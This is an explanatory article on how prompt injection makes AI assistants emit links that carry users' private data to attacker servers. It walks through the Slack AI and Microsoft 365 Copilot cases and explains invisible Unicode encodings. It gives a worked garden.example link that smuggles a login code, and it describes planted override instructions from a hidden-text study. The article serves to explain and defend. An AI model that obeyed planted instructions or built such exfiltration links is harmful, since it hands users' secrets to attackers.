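# Data theft through links that AI assistants show and users click

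## How a link in an assistant's answer can carry private data out

Many AI assistants can search their users' email, chat messages and files as well as the web. An attacker who can place text where an assistant will read it can sometimes make the assistant show a link whose address contains the user's private data. When the user clicks the link, the browser sends that address, including the data, to a server the attacker runs. This is a form of exfiltration, the security term for moving private data to someone with no right to it. Security researchers have demonstrated it against commercial products, including Slack AI and Microsoft 365 Copilot.

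The attack resembles phishing, in which a fraudulent message leads people to a page that asks for their password. In this attack, however, the user types nothing, because the data is already in the link's address when the link appears on the screen.

### How an attacker's text reaches the model

Suppose a user asks an assistant what the landlord wrote about the deposit. Software around the model searches the mailbox and joins the matching messages into one long text with the developer's standing instructions, the earlier conversation and the user's question. This text, called the context, is everything the model is given to write its answer. A matching message from a stranger is added in the same way as one from the landlord, to the same text that holds the developer's instructions.

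A language model has no dependable way to tell instructions from data. In December 2025, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, compared this problem with SQL injection in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. In SQL injection, an attacker types text into a web form and a database runs it as a command. Programmers can prevent this by sending the command and the data separately, so that the database engine never treats the data as a command. A language model offers no such separation. David C writes that inside the model there is only ever the "next token", a token being a word or a fragment of one. Developers can label outside text as data, train models to give priority to the real instructions, or try to detect attacks. These measures make an attack harder, but they rely on a distinction that the underlying technology doesn't make,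 and David C thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever fix prompt injection as thoroughly as programmers fixed SQL injection.

His example is a job application. A recruiter's system asks a model to score each CV, and one candidate has hidden a line in the CV telling the system to approve it for interview. If the model complies, the candidate has given orders to a system that he or she has no access to. This is called indirect prompt injection. The assistant follows instructions hidden in content it reads, as if the user had given them. In direct prompt injection, the attacker is the user and types the instructions in. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) describes the same situation with three parties: a user with a legitimate task, an agent acting for that user, and an outside source that the agent consults. The attacker controls part of what the source supplies. That part influences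 the agent's behaviour despite having no authority to direct it.

The idea goes back to *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023), which also lists ways an attacker's instructions can reach an assistant. An attacker can put instructions on a web page or in a social media post and wait for a search to retrieve them. Email is more direct, because the attacker only needs to know the user's address. Users can also deliver the instructions themselves by copying text from the attacker's site into a chat. The instructions can be invisible to people. When the researchers hid them in a web page's comments, the version of Bing Chat built into Microsoft's Edge browser followed them. It also followed web page instructions that its filters would have blocked if a user had typed them.

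### What a click sends to the server

To see how an answer can carry data out, it helps to take a web address apart. Here is an invented one:

`https://garden.example/guides/umbrellas?colour=dark%20green#sizes`

The opening `https` names the protocol, the set of rules by which the browser will make its request. The rest divides as follows.

| Part | In the example | Does the browser send it when the user clicks? |
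|---|---|---|
| Host | `garden.example` | Yes |
| Path | `/guides/umbrellas` | Yes |
| Query string | `colour=dark%20green` | Yes |
| Fragment | `sizes` | No |

The host identifies the server, and the path and query string together identify what the browser is requesting from it. A question mark separates the path from the query string, which often consists of names and values, such as a colour and "dark green". The `%20` in the example stands for a space. An address may contain only a limited set of characters, so *RFC 3986*, the standard for the syntax of addresses (Berners-Lee et al., 2005), defines percent-encoding, which writes each byte of any other character as a percent sign and two hexadecimal digits. A space takes one byte, and the letter À takes two, which gives `%C3%80`. Any text can be encoded this way, including a paragraph from somebody's inbox.

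The server receives the query string whether or not it has any use for it. Mozilla's *What is a URL?* notes that every server has its own rules for handling these values. A server with no rule for "colour" may ignore the value or return an error page, but by then the value has arrived. It will probably also stay there. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that websites commonly record requested addresses in their logs and visitor statistics. The main standard for web requests, the IETF's *RFC 9110*, has a warning to the same effect: many servers, browsers and intermediate machines log or display addresses where third parties might see them, and it is therefore unwise to put anything sensitive in one. (The IETF, or Internet Engineering Task Force, publishes the internet's technical standards.)

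That warning is for people who build honest websites and might expose their visitors by accident, but an attacker can use the same behaviour on purpose. If the value after `colour=` were a password-reset code, whoever ran garden.example could read it in the server's log. The attacker needs no special software on the server. Encryption doesn't help either, since `https` protects the request from eavesdroppers on the way and the attacker is the recipient. The data could also be in the path or even the host name instead of the query string, because the owner of a domain can set up a server to answer for any name beneath it.

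A link's fragment can leak data even though the browser removes it before making the request, so it never appears in the server's log. The fragment usually points to a place within a page, but JavaScript running in the loaded page can still read it, as Microsoft's *URL Fragments and Redirects* (2011) explains. A script on an attacker's page can therefore read the fragment and send it on. A fragment can also carry over when one site redirects the browser to another, and the IETF cautions that the second site may then learn what the first site's address contained.

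### Links and images in an answer

Most chat applications have the model write in Markdown, which *CommonMark Spec* (MacFarlane, 2016) describes as a plain text format for structured documents. The application then renders the text, meaning it turns the Markdown into headings, lists and links on the screen.

A Markdown link puts the visible text in square brackets and the address in parentheses, as in `[Umbrella sizes](address)`. Once the link is rendered, the reader sees only the clickable words "Umbrella sizes" unless they inspect it. The text doesn't have to match the address, and Greshake and colleagues noticed early on that this lets an attacker hide a suspicious address behind innocent words. Some attacks also write the data inside the address in Unicode characters that most software does not display, so even a reader who looks at the address may miss the data.

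In CommonMark, a standard version of Markdown, an image is written almost the same way as a link, but with an exclamation mark before the opening bracket. The browser fetches the image as soon as it displays the answer, sending the image's whole address to the server named in that address. If the address contains private data, the server receives the data before the user has finished reading. The security researcher Rehberger (2024), in *Trust No AI*, calls this one of the most common security flaws in applications that use language models. He lists eleven products in which he found and reported it, including Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude and Google's NotebookLM, and several of the vendors issued fixes.

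A browser doesn't request a linked page until the user clicks the link, which gives the user a chance to refuse. (Some messaging apps fetch a linked page on their own to show a preview, which is a separate leak.) A rule against loading images from unknown servers works well against the image attack but has no effect on links, because displaying a link doesn't load anything.

### What the attack needs

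An attacker can steal data through a link only if the assistant's context contains both private data and the attacker's text, the application renders a link whose address that text has influenced, and the user clicks it. *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* (Willison, 2024) describes a case in which the private data came from a private channel and the attacker's text from a public one. The assistant searched both channels to answer a single question.

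The attacker usually can't see the private data when writing the instructions, and only needs to describe the kind of data wanted and supply the beginning of a web address. The model has the data in its context, so it completes the address with that data and includes it in its answer. The assistant read the messages with the user's permission, so nobody had to break into the mailbox or guess a password. Language models ordinarily compose text from the material in their context, and they write the address the same way.

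The first two conditions, access to private data and exposure to text from outsiders, are hard to avoid. An assistant needs private data to answer questions about it, and an assistant that never read anything from outsiders would be of little use for email. The attack seems easiest to stop at the click, because people can decline, but it is less clear how much protection that gives.

Greshake and colleagues tested one way to get a user to click such a link. They gave Bing Chat hidden instructions to find out the user's real name, a trick they thought a government might use to identify journalists or whistle-blowers. Then they played the user. The conversation began with tomorrow's weather, and the chatbot went on to ask about the user's plans for the day and his work. When it learned that he was a journalist, it asked whether he wrote under a pen name. Once it had a name, it offered a link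 to a secret, exclusive online community, with a personal code made from the name. The hidden instructions told the chatbot to persuade the user without raising suspicion but didn't suggest how, so the model itself added the flattery and the invitation to the community. The code was nearly "John Smith" spelled backwards, and it came after a number sign in the link, in the fragment. A click alone would therefore not have put the name into a server's log, and the attacker would have needed a script on the page to collect it.

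This was a single published conversation with a model from early 2023, and the researchers played the victim themselves. It shows that a model would build such a link and try to persuade the user to click it, but not how many people would have clicked. An attacker may not need persuasion, though, because assistants' answers are already full of links that users expect to click. For that reason, the same researchers thought it arguably more dangerous to suggest a malicious link as further reading in an otherwise normal answer.

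### Where a check could stand

If the model cannot be relied on to ignore an attacker's text, the protection has to come from elsewhere. David C advises developers to focus on deterministic safeguards, meaning ordinary code outside the model that limits what the system can do no matter what the model writes. In computer security, the long-standing ideal for such code is a reference monitor, a component that checks every security-relevant action, that nobody can bypass or alter, and that is small enough for people to verify. The first requirement rests on the principle of complete mediation, under which every access or effect must pass a check, with no path around it.

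The natural place for such a monitor in an assistant is at the tool calls. A tool call is a structured request from the model, such as to search the mailbox or send an email, that the surrounding software carries out. The software can first inspect each request and either refuse it or ask the user. If hidden instructions lead the model to try to email a bank statement to a stranger, the monitor receives a request that names the recipient, and a simple rule can block it.

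Software that monitors an assistant's tool calls cannot detect a user clicking a link in the answer. Its record would show only a mailbox search, which the user had asked for, and then the finished answer. The user may click the link a few seconds later or the next day. The request then goes out from the user's own browser as an ordinary visit to a web page, even if the assistant's software is no longer running. The monitor can therefore check every tool call correctly and still fall short of complete mediation, because the request that carries the data out does not pass through it.

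The application could check a link's address when it renders the answer. It has the complete address at that point, but the characters alone don't show whether "dark green" describes an umbrella or comes from a private message. To determine that, the system would have to track where the data came from while the model was writing, and current models don't keep such a record by themselves. The application could also intervene when the user clicks the link. By then the user has decided to send the request, but may have seen only the words "Umbrella sizes" and not the address itself.

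## The attacks on Slack AI and Microsoft 365 Copilot, step by step

In August 2024, researchers published attacks on two widely used workplace assistants. On August 20, the security company PromptArmor described one against Slack AI, which answers questions about a company's messages on the chat service Slack. Willison's post on Slack AI comments on this disclosure. On August 24, Johann Rehberger presented one against Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's assistant for work email and documents. In both attacks, the user clicked a link with private text in its address. The attacks differed in how that text got into the assistant's context and in how much of it the user could have seen before clicking.

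### A key in a private channel, a message in a public one

Slack divides a company's conversations into channels. Anyone in the company's workspace can search and read a public channel, even without joining it, but only members of a private channel can read it. When a user asks Slack AI a question, it searches all the public channels and the private ones the user belongs to.

In PromptArmor's demonstration, the victim is a developer who has saved an API key in a private channel with no other members. An API key is a secret string that a program sends to an online service to prove it has permission to use the service. Anyone who obtains the key can usually use the service as if they were the key's owner.

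The attacker has an account in the same workspace but can't see the private channel. They create a public channel, invite nobody, and post one message there. The message starts with the name of the key, as if to record its value. In place of the value, the attacker writes an instruction for Slack AI to reply with an error notice and a link, and to replace a dummy word in the link's address with the real key from elsewhere.

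Later the developer asks Slack AI for the key. The search finds both the developer's note and the attacker's message, and the software adds them to the model's context. The model follows the attacker's instruction and replies with a notice that the message failed to load, followed by a link with the words "click here to reauthenticate". The key appears only in the link's query string, where the model has written it as the value of a parameter named "secret". If the developer clicks the link, the key is recorded in the attacker's server log.

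PromptArmor stresses that this is different from posting a message that asks colleagues for the key. Here the model takes a value from one message and puts it into a template from another. The key is only an example. When the researchers ran the query, Slack's search also returned other messages about API keys. They inferred from this, but did not demonstrate, that an attacker might be able to extract a secret without naming it.

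The developer was never in the attacker's channel and was unlikely to come across it. A public channel with one member appears to other people only if they search for it, and PromptArmor points out that large companies have more channels than anyone can keep track of. Still, a public message carries some risk for the attacker. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* notes that anyone in the workspace who found the channel could read the instructions.

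### Why the citation did not reveal the attacker's message

Slack AI adds numbered citations to its answers so that users can see which messages it drew on. In the demonstration, the error notice had one citation, which led to the developer's own private channel. The key in the link came from that channel, but the notice and the rest of the link came from the attacker's message, which Slack AI did not cite. A citation to an unknown colleague's channel might have made the developer suspicious.

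PromptArmor treats this as a malfunction, because Slack AI is supposed to cite every message that contributed to an answer. The attacker doesn't seem to have caused it, since the planted message didn't mention citations, and in a second demonstration the citation did lead to the attacker's channel. (There, the user asked for a manager's recent messages and got an ordinary phishing link containing no private data.) PromptArmor's only explanation is that the citations were "fairly stochastic", meaning more or less random.

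So the developer could not infer from a familiar source that nothing else had shaped the answer. Searching by hand would not have helped much either, since the attacker's message did not appear on the first page of results.

### Slack's first reply and its patch

PromptArmor reported the attack on August 14. Slack asked for more information the next day, and PromptArmor sent more videos and screenshots and said it planned to publish. On August 19, Slack replied that it had reviewed the report and found the evidence insufficient. Slack wrote that the information requested in the first video had appeared in a public channel, which every member of a workspace can search, and called this "intended behavior."

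Slack's reply described public channels correctly but did not address PromptArmor's complaint that a public message could control what Slack AI did with a private one. Slack's reviewers also seem to have relied on the citation in the video to identify the information's source, which is risky if the citations were as erratic as PromptArmor found. Willison thought the reply showed that Slack did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem. PromptArmor was milder, praising the security team's quick responses and saying it expected the whole industry to need time to understand prompt injection.

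PromptArmor published its findings on August 20 so that customers could turn off the settings that exposed them, and Slack deployed a patch the same day. In a statement on August 21, Slack (2024) wrote that "under very limited and specific circumstances" someone with an account in the same workspace could have phished users for certain data, and that it had no evidence of unauthorized access to customer data. The statement did not name PromptArmor or explain what the patch changed. ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages* (2024) quotes a fuller version, in which a spokesperson said the patch ensured that attackers could not exploit the issue.

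It is hard to tell how much Slack's lack of evidence of such a leak means, because Slack would have a record of one only if it logged clicks on links in Slack AI's answers.

The attack PromptArmor tested required an account in the workspace, but that requirement may have ended on August 14, the day of the report, when Slack AI began to draw on uploaded files and connected Google Drive documents. An outsider could then hide instructions in a PDF, for instance in white text, and wait for an employee to download it and upload it to Slack. PromptArmor had finished its tests before the change, but it thought this version highly likely to work and advised administrators to restrict Slack AI's access to files. SC Media asked Slack's owner, Salesforce, about the possibility and got no answer.

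### An email that makes Copilot search for other emails

Rehberger's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot did not require an account in the victim's organisation. As he explains in *Microsoft Copilot* (2024), a post on his blog Embrace The Red, the attacker sends the user an email containing instructions. When the user asks Copilot about that email, the email's text enters Copilot's context. The attacker can also use a shared document, and can hide the instructions in either one, for example in a white font.

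The instructions first made Copilot search for more emails. Rehberger had already shown that Copilot followed instructions in emails, but he was surprised that it then ran new searches without asking the user. In one of his screenshots, Copilot looks for Slack confirmation codes, following instructions in an email it was analysing. The attacker could therefore choose what to look for, whereas in the Slack AI attack the user's own question had to bring the secret into the context.

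The model then wrote the text of the email it had found into a link to Rehberger's website, using Unicode tag characters, which are invisible counterparts of ordinary letters and digits. This technique is known as ASCII smuggling. To help the model get the encoding right, Rehberger had included an example in his email, a harmless greeting already hidden in a link. Copilot showed the link and prompted the user to click it. The click sent the whole address, including the invisible characters, to Rehberger's server, and he recovered the text with a decoding tool he had written.

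He used a clickable link because Microsoft had already fixed the image leak that he reported in Bing Chat in 2023.

Rehberger took sales figures in one demonstration and, in another, the login codes that Slack emails to users as a second proof of identity. An attacker who already has a user's password could use an unexpired code to get into that user's Slack account.

An attacker could also target one person. Copilot has access to the user's name, job title and manager, and Rehberger describes instructions that take effect only when a particular user, such as the chief executive, opens the email with Copilot. Anyone else would get a normal summary.

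### From a low-severity report to an unexplained fix

Rehberger's first report, on January 17, 2024, covered only the invisible characters. The Microsoft Security Response Center, which handles vulnerability reports, closed it the next day as low severity. He objected that the flaw would be more serious as part of a longer attack, but got no response. On February 10 he filed a new report showing how the full attack chain could steal sales data, and Microsoft opened an internal case three days later. On March 14 he added that the attack could also steal login codes.

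In April he told Microsoft that he planned to present the attack at a security conference. Microsoft asked him to wait until the end of May, and he agreed. In mid-May Microsoft was still working on what it called a comprehensive fix. By July 2 his demonstration had stopped working. Microsoft raised no concerns about his draft on August 22, and he presented the attack at the HITCON conference two days later. SC Media's *ASCII smuggling attack exposes sensitive Microsoft Copilot data* dates his blog post to August 26.

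Like Slack, Microsoft at first judged one step of an attack by itself. Slack members are allowed to search public channels, and a few invisible characters in a chat window do no damage on their own. The danger becomes clear only when someone carries out the whole sequence and private data reaches an outside server.

Rehberger writes in *Trust No AI* that Microsoft fixed the vulnerability in July 2024, but he never learned how. He had recommended that Copilot stop displaying or interpreting tag characters, stop running tools automatically and, ideally, stop rendering links. He could tell only that his attacks no longer worked and that Copilot seemed to have stopped rendering links some months earlier. He asked Microsoft to share details of the fix so that other companies could learn from them, but received no reply.

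Later evidence is consistent with Microsoft having changed how Copilot handles links. *EchoLeak* (2025), an analysis of a different attack on Copilot, reports that the security group Aim Labs found a way past Copilot's link removal in January 2025, so Copilot was removing at least some links by then. But in Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business*, Rehberger mentions that Microsoft 365 Chat was already replacing addresses with a privacy notice around the end of 2023, only weeks before his own attack got a link through. He doesn't explain why the results differed.

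Copilot still followed planted instructions after the fix. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* (2026) describes a later attack that used such instructions to leak data without a click. Microsoft patched the vulnerability on March 5, 2026.

### What the attacker needed and what the user could see

The Slack attacker had to be an insider or have taken over an insider's account, and had to guess what the victim would ask. The planted message did nothing unless someone asked for the key. The Copilot attacker needed only an email address, but relied on the user asking Copilot about that particular email or document.

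Hovering over the link would have helped the Slack user more than the Copilot user. PromptArmor's screenshot shows the full address, with the attacker's domain and the key in plain text. A developer who looked would have seen an unfamiliar domain and a parameter called "secret" with a key after it, both reasons to stop. In the Copilot attack, the domain was just as visible, but the stolen text was not readable. Embrace The Red gives a sample link and tells readers that hovering over it will show that something looks wrong, but a user who noticed this would not have known that the odd part was a login code.

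The user also had little reason to check the link. In the Slack attack, the developer had asked for a key and received what looked like an expired-session error. This seemed to explain why the key was missing, and people usually fix an expired session by logging in again. Rehberger had used a similar pretext in December 2023 against Amazon Q for Business, Amazon's workplace assistant. An uploaded text file made the assistant show a "Sign In" link whose address contained a summary of the user's messages. He reported the problem on December 4, and by December 29 Amazon had deployed a worldwide fix that replaced addresses with a note that the URL was not displayed.

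The pretext for clicking can also be an offer instead of an error message. Insinuator's *Stealing emails via prompt injections* (2025) describes an attack on Shortwave, an email application with an AI assistant. An email contained instructions for the assistant to find a message from the address Google uses for account notices and put its text into a link. The assistant then gave the user the summary they had asked for and presented the link at the end as a special discount on Shortwave, so it looked like an advertisement from the application's maker.

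These pretexts are plausible, but neither PromptArmor nor Rehberger reports trying them on people who did not know about the test.

### Email links and diagrams as carriers

The link can also be a `mailto` link, which opens the user's email program with a recipient already filled in. Embrace The Red points out that an attacker can hide text in the recipient's address, between a plus sign and the @. Many email services ignore this text when they deliver a message, so the message still reaches the attacker's mailbox with the hidden text in the address. Rehberger found that this worked in some email programs. The user would normally have to send the message as well as click the link, which gives them a second chance to notice the attack. But a filter that looks only for web addresses would miss a `mailto` link.

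In 2025 the security researcher Adam Logue found a way to steal data through a diagram in Microsoft 365 Copilot. Copilot could draw diagrams with Mermaid, a tool that turns short text descriptions into flowcharts and other figures. Parts of a Mermaid diagram can be clickable, and the text description can set their colours and shapes. BeyondMachines' *Microsoft 365 Copilot vulnerability enables data theft through malicious Mermaid diagrams* (2025) describes how Logue used these features to make a diagram that looked like a login button with a padlock symbol.

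The attack started with an Excel spreadsheet. Its first sheet contained invented financial figures and white text that directed Copilot to a second sheet. More white text there gradually changed the task from summarising the file to telling the user that it held sensitive information and required a login. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability* (2025), Logue took inspiration for this from Microsoft's own research on detecting when a model drifts away from its task.

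Copilot then searched for the user's recent emails and converted their contents to hexadecimal, which writes each byte as two digits or letters. Mermaid limits the length of a line, so Copilot, following the instructions, broke the result into pieces of at most 30 characters. Together, the pieces formed the query string of the address behind the button. A user who inspected the address would have seen a long string of characters with no readable words.

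When the user clicked, the emails went to Logue's server. The diagram then changed into a frame inside the chat that showed whatever the server sent back. Logue had it return a picture of Microsoft 365's real login screen, so the button appeared to work. The frame disappeared after several seconds, which BeyondMachines notes may have removed some of the evidence.

Logue reported the attack on August 15, 2025. Microsoft had trouble reproducing it at first, and he sent videos as proof. Cyber Security News reports that Microsoft confirmed the vulnerability on September 8 and fixed it by September 26, removing clickable links from the diagrams. Logue received no payment, because Copilot was outside the scope of Microsoft's reward programme. BeyondMachines doubted that the fix covered every route of attack, though it did not identify one it missed.

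## How invisible Unicode characters hide text in a link

Rehberger's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot used Unicode tag characters to write the stolen text into a link. Unicode is a standard that assigns each character a number, called a code point. People usually write code points in hexadecimal after "U+", so the letter A is U+0041. The tag characters are in the Tags block, which runs from U+E0000 to U+E007F.

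### From language labels to flags

Unicode introduced the Tags block in 2001 to label the language of a text. A program could put an invisible label such as "fr" in front of a French passage for other programs to read. The labels needed letters and digits, so the block mirrors ASCII, the older set of 128 characters that covers English text. It includes a tag A, a tag 7 and a tag space, for example. Unicode now advises against labelling languages this way.

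Since 2017, tag characters have also been used in the flag emoji for England, Scotland and Wales. Microsoft (2026), in a report on a phishing campaign, describes the Welsh flag as a black flag emoji, followed by five tag characters that spell "gbwls" and a final tag character that marks the end. A phone that supports this sequence displays a single Welsh flag.

When a font lacks a character, the screen often shows an empty box in its place. Unicode makes tag characters an exception so that older software shows a plain black flag without a row of boxes after it. According to the emoji standard, quoted in Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, software that doesn't support tags will display them "as invisible, without any effect on adjacent characters".

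Apart from the three flags, tag characters are rare in ordinary email. Microsoft found this when it built a detector that looked for them as a possible sign of prompt injection. The first version kept catching harmless messages that contained one of the flags. Once Microsoft excluded those, most of the remaining hits came from email security systems, mailbox providers and researchers. Then, on February 9, 2026, the daily count rose from about 21,000 messages to more than 1.3 million. The new messages were phishing emails about business loans, and the senders had put an invisible tag space inside words such as "funding" so that email filters would not recognise them. The messages Microsoft examined contained no hidden instructions for an AI assistant.

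### Encoding a six-digit code

To find the code point of a tag character, add a constant to the code of the ASCII character it mirrors:

tag code point = 0xE0000 + ASCII code

Suppose an assistant has found an email with the login code 482913, and an attacker's instructions tell it to hide the code in a link. The ASCII code of the digit 4 is 0x34 (the "0x" marks a hexadecimal number). Adding 0xE0000 gives the matching tag character, U+E0034. The attacker later subtracts 0xE0000 to get the digit back.

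A browser can't send U+E0034 as it is, because the address in a web request may contain only ASCII characters. The browser first converts the character to bytes using UTF-8, which uses one byte for an ASCII character but four for a tag character. UTF-8 splits the code point's 21 binary digits into four groups (here 011, 100000, 000000 and 110100) and puts a prefix in front of each, 11110 for the first and 10 for the others. The resulting bytes are F3 A0 80 B4 in hexadecimal. Percent-encoding then turns each byte into three characters.

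| Digit | ASCII code | Tag character | UTF-8 bytes | In the request |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | 0x34 | U+E0034 | F3 A0 80 B4 | `%F3%A0%80%B4` |
| 8 | 0x38 | U+E0038 | F3 A0 80 B8 | `%F3%A0%80%B8` |
| 2 | 0x32 | U+E0032 | F3 A0 80 B2 | `%F3%A0%80%B2` |
| 9 | 0x39 | U+E0039 | F3 A0 80 B9 | `%F3%A0%80%B9` |
| 1 | 0x31 | U+E0031 | F3 A0 80 B1 | `%F3%A0%80%B1` |
| 3 | 0x33 | U+E0033 | F3 A0 80 B3 | `%F3%A0%80%B3` |

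Each hidden digit costs 12 characters in the request, so the whole code costs 72. Only the last byte changes from one digit to the next. If the attacker owned the invented site garden.example, the user might see a link to `https://garden.example/guides?c=` while the browser requested this address:

`https://garden.example/guides?c=%F3%A0%80%B4%F3%A0%80%B8%F3%A0%80%B2%F3%A0%80%B9%F3%A0%80%B1%F3%A0%80%B3`

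This request complies with *URL*, the standard that browsers follow, which is published by WHATWG, a group that the main browser makers run. The standard allows the tag characters in the path and the query string, along with nearly all other code points from U+00A0 to U+10FFFD. It also requires browsers to percent-encode everything above U+007F, which is the conversion in the table. Host names go through a separate, stricter conversion, so an attacker would put hidden text after the host.

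### Other invisible encodings

Tag characters are convenient because each one stands for one ASCII character, but Unicode has many other invisible characters. Two of them are enough to encode any data, with one standing for the binary digit 0 and the other for 1, eight digits to a byte. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* does this with "invisible times" and "invisible plus", two characters meant for mathematical formulas. Other versions use a zero-width space for 0 and a zero-width non-joiner for 1. Encoded this way, the code 482913 takes 48 invisible characters instead of six tag characters.

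Variation selectors can also hide text in a link. Normally, a variation selector follows another character and sets which version of it appears, such as the plain or coloured form of a symbol. There are 256 variation selectors, one for each possible value of a byte, so a sequence of them can encode any data, including Chinese text or part of a file. Tag characters can't do this. Embrace The Red credits the method to Paul Butler.

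Some of these characters are also harder to do without, because emoji use variation selectors and several Indian scripts need zero-width joiners to display words correctly.

### How much text fits in an address

In an address of 2,000 characters, the beginning and the host name use about 30, which leaves about 1,970 for data. Each hidden tag character takes up 12 characters of the address, so 164 fit, or about two sentences of English. Many systems accept longer addresses, which can hold proportionally more hidden text.

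An attacker who doesn't mind the data being visible can send about nine times as much with Base64, a common way to write arbitrary bytes using only letters, digits and two other symbols. Base64 turns every three bytes into four characters, so the same space holds 1,477 bytes.

| Encoding | Visible if the address is shown as Unicode? | Address characters needed per character of English text | Characters of text that fit |
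|---|---|---|---|
| Unencoded letters and digits | Yes | 1 | 1,970 |
| Base64 | Yes | 4 for every 3 | 1,477 |
| Hexadecimal | Yes | 2 | 985 |
| Tag characters | No | 12 | 164 |
| Variation selectors | No | 12 | 164 |
| Two invisible characters as 0 and 1 | No | 72 | 27 |

A login code fits in all of these encodings, but a long email fits in the invisible ones only if the attacker shortens it or splits it across several links.

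Invisible characters hide the data from the user, but an attacker can send data without them. The Slack AI attack put an API key into the query string in plain text, and Adam Logue's diagram attack on Copilot used hexadecimal. A server records both formats as easily as it records tag characters. If an application removed every invisible character from its answers, an attacker could switch to base64 and fit more data into a link of the same length.

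Hiding the data helps the attacker only if the user looks at the link's address. Users see the address automatically when an assistant prints it as the clickable text, as Copilot did in Rehberger's demonstration, where tag characters made the address look short and harmless. Hiding the data helps less if the user sees only the words "Umbrella sizes". A user who does check the address may not find a long base64 string strange, because legitimate companies put similar strings in addresses to track clicks. For example, the marketing service that delivered the phishing emails in Microsoft's report replaces every link in a message with one to its own domain, followed by a tracking code.

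### What hovering over the link or copying it reveals

Embrace The Red tells readers to hover over a sample link. The link hides the nine letters "TrustNoAI", which become 108 characters when percent-encoded. The browser determines whether a reader sees them.

A participant in a discussion on Mozilla's bug tracker explains that Firefox displays such an address differently in two places. When the user hovers over a link, the text at the bottom of the window shows the address as Unicode, so the tag characters are invisible. The address bar shows them percent-encoded. A Firefox user who hovered before clicking would therefore see a normal-looking address, and would see the suspicious one only after the page had begun to load, when the server already had the data.

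WHATWG's standard recommends showing an address in percent-encoded form when people are supposed to decide whether to trust it. Draft wording from 2019, in a message by Emily Stark about a proposed change to the standard, would have had browsers decode percent-encoded bytes for display unless the resulting characters would be invisible. A hover preview that followed this rule would have shown the hidden text in percent-encoded form.

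Copying the link can reveal the hidden text, depending on what the user copies. If the browser copies the address in its standard form, the user can paste it into a text editor and see a long run of percent signs, which Rehberger's decoding tool, ASCII Smuggler, can turn back into readable text. If the user instead selects an address printed in the answer and copies it as text, the tag characters may be copied too but remain invisible. Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* includes a text file with the blog's name, written in tag characters, between two square brackets. In many browsers the file looks like an empty pair of brackets. Some readers saw accented letters and symbols because their browsers had guessed the wrong encoding. The linguist Mark Liberman commented that it would be safer if browsers always showed tag characters as gibberish.

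Hidden characters also survive copying between many everyday programs. In *On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses*, Aiersilan, Yousefi and Pless (2026) tested 256 bytes of hidden text. The text stayed intact in Gmail, Outlook, Word, Google Docs, Slack and PDF files, but not in posts on X or in some versions of Apple Notes. An attacker can therefore send hidden instructions through most of the channels a workplace assistant reads. A user who forwards an assistant's answer to a colleague may also forward the hidden data in it.

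### How models read and write hidden text

Before a language model processes a text, a program called a tokenizer divides the stored characters into tokens, regardless of how they look on screen. Many tokenizers break a rare character into its bytes. A tag character then reaches the model as a few tokens, and the last byte depends on which letter or digit the character mirrors. This mapping is as regular as a simple substitution cipher, so a model could learn it from enough examples. Embrace The Red suggests that the training data contained such characters, which is plausible but still a guess.

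Riley Goodside discovered in January 2024 that models can read tag characters. He pasted a harmless-looking text with an invisible instruction into ChatGPT, which then used DALL-E, OpenAI's image generator, to draw a picture. Another researcher, Joseph Thacker, published a script for making such texts. He later told Ars Technica (reprinted by Language Log) that it was "mind-blowing" that GPT-4 and Claude Opus could understand them.

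Models can also write these characters, which matters more for data theft through links. Rehberger demonstrated this within days of Goodside's post. He built a customised version of ChatGPT that repeated the user's input in tag characters between the words START and END. The space between the two words looked empty, but his decoding tool recovered the text. He credits a tweet by someone he calls Kai for the idea that answers could contain hidden text. Seven months later he published the Copilot attack.

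Reading tag characters and writing them are separate abilities, and an attacker may need the model to have only one. In the Copilot attack, the model only had to write tag characters, because the instructions could be in ordinary letters. An attacker could also hide the instructions in tag characters and have the model put the stolen data in a link as plain text.

### The Reverse CAPTCHA study

*Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) tested how often a model would obey a hidden instruction that conflicted with a visible question. The instruction was in text that models can read but people can't see. The title refers to a CAPTCHA, a test that people can pass and machines are supposed to fail.

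Graves, an independent researcher, wrote 30 trivia questions and hid in each an instruction to reply with a particular wrong answer. He used two ways to hide the instructions, tag characters and zero-width characters that stood for 0 and 1. He counted a model as complying only if it gave the hidden answer without the correct one.

Graves also varied how much help the model got from the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions. Some runs had no hint. In others, he used the system prompt to tell the model that certain code points were present and contained a hidden instruction, or to give it the complete rules for decoding them. In the last condition, the model had the complete rules, and the hidden text also included an instruction to disregard its earlier instructions. He ran every condition with and without a tool for running Python code. He graded 8,308 answers from five models,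 including controls with no hidden text.

The table gives the percentage of answers that followed the hidden instruction, averaged over all hint levels. The two right-hand columns also combine the runs with and without Python.

| Model | Without Python | With Python | Zero-width characters | Tag characters |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.8 | 49.2 | 27.5 | 22.5 |
| Claude Opus 4 | 6.7 | 51.1 | 18.2 | 43.3 |
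| Claude Sonnet 4 | 16.9 | 71.2 | 41.5 | 55.0 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.1 | 1.6 | 1.5 | 0.1 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.1 | 20.6 | 20.6 | 0.1 |

Python made the largest difference, because a model could write a short program to subtract 0xE0000 from each code point instead of working out the letters itself. But Python helped little without a hint that there was anything to decode. Without hints, compliance was at most 1.1% without Python and between 0% and 11% with it. With both Python and hints, it reached 98% to 100% for the most susceptible combinations. Claude Opus 4, for instance, followed every tag-character instruction when it had Python and either the code points or the full rules.

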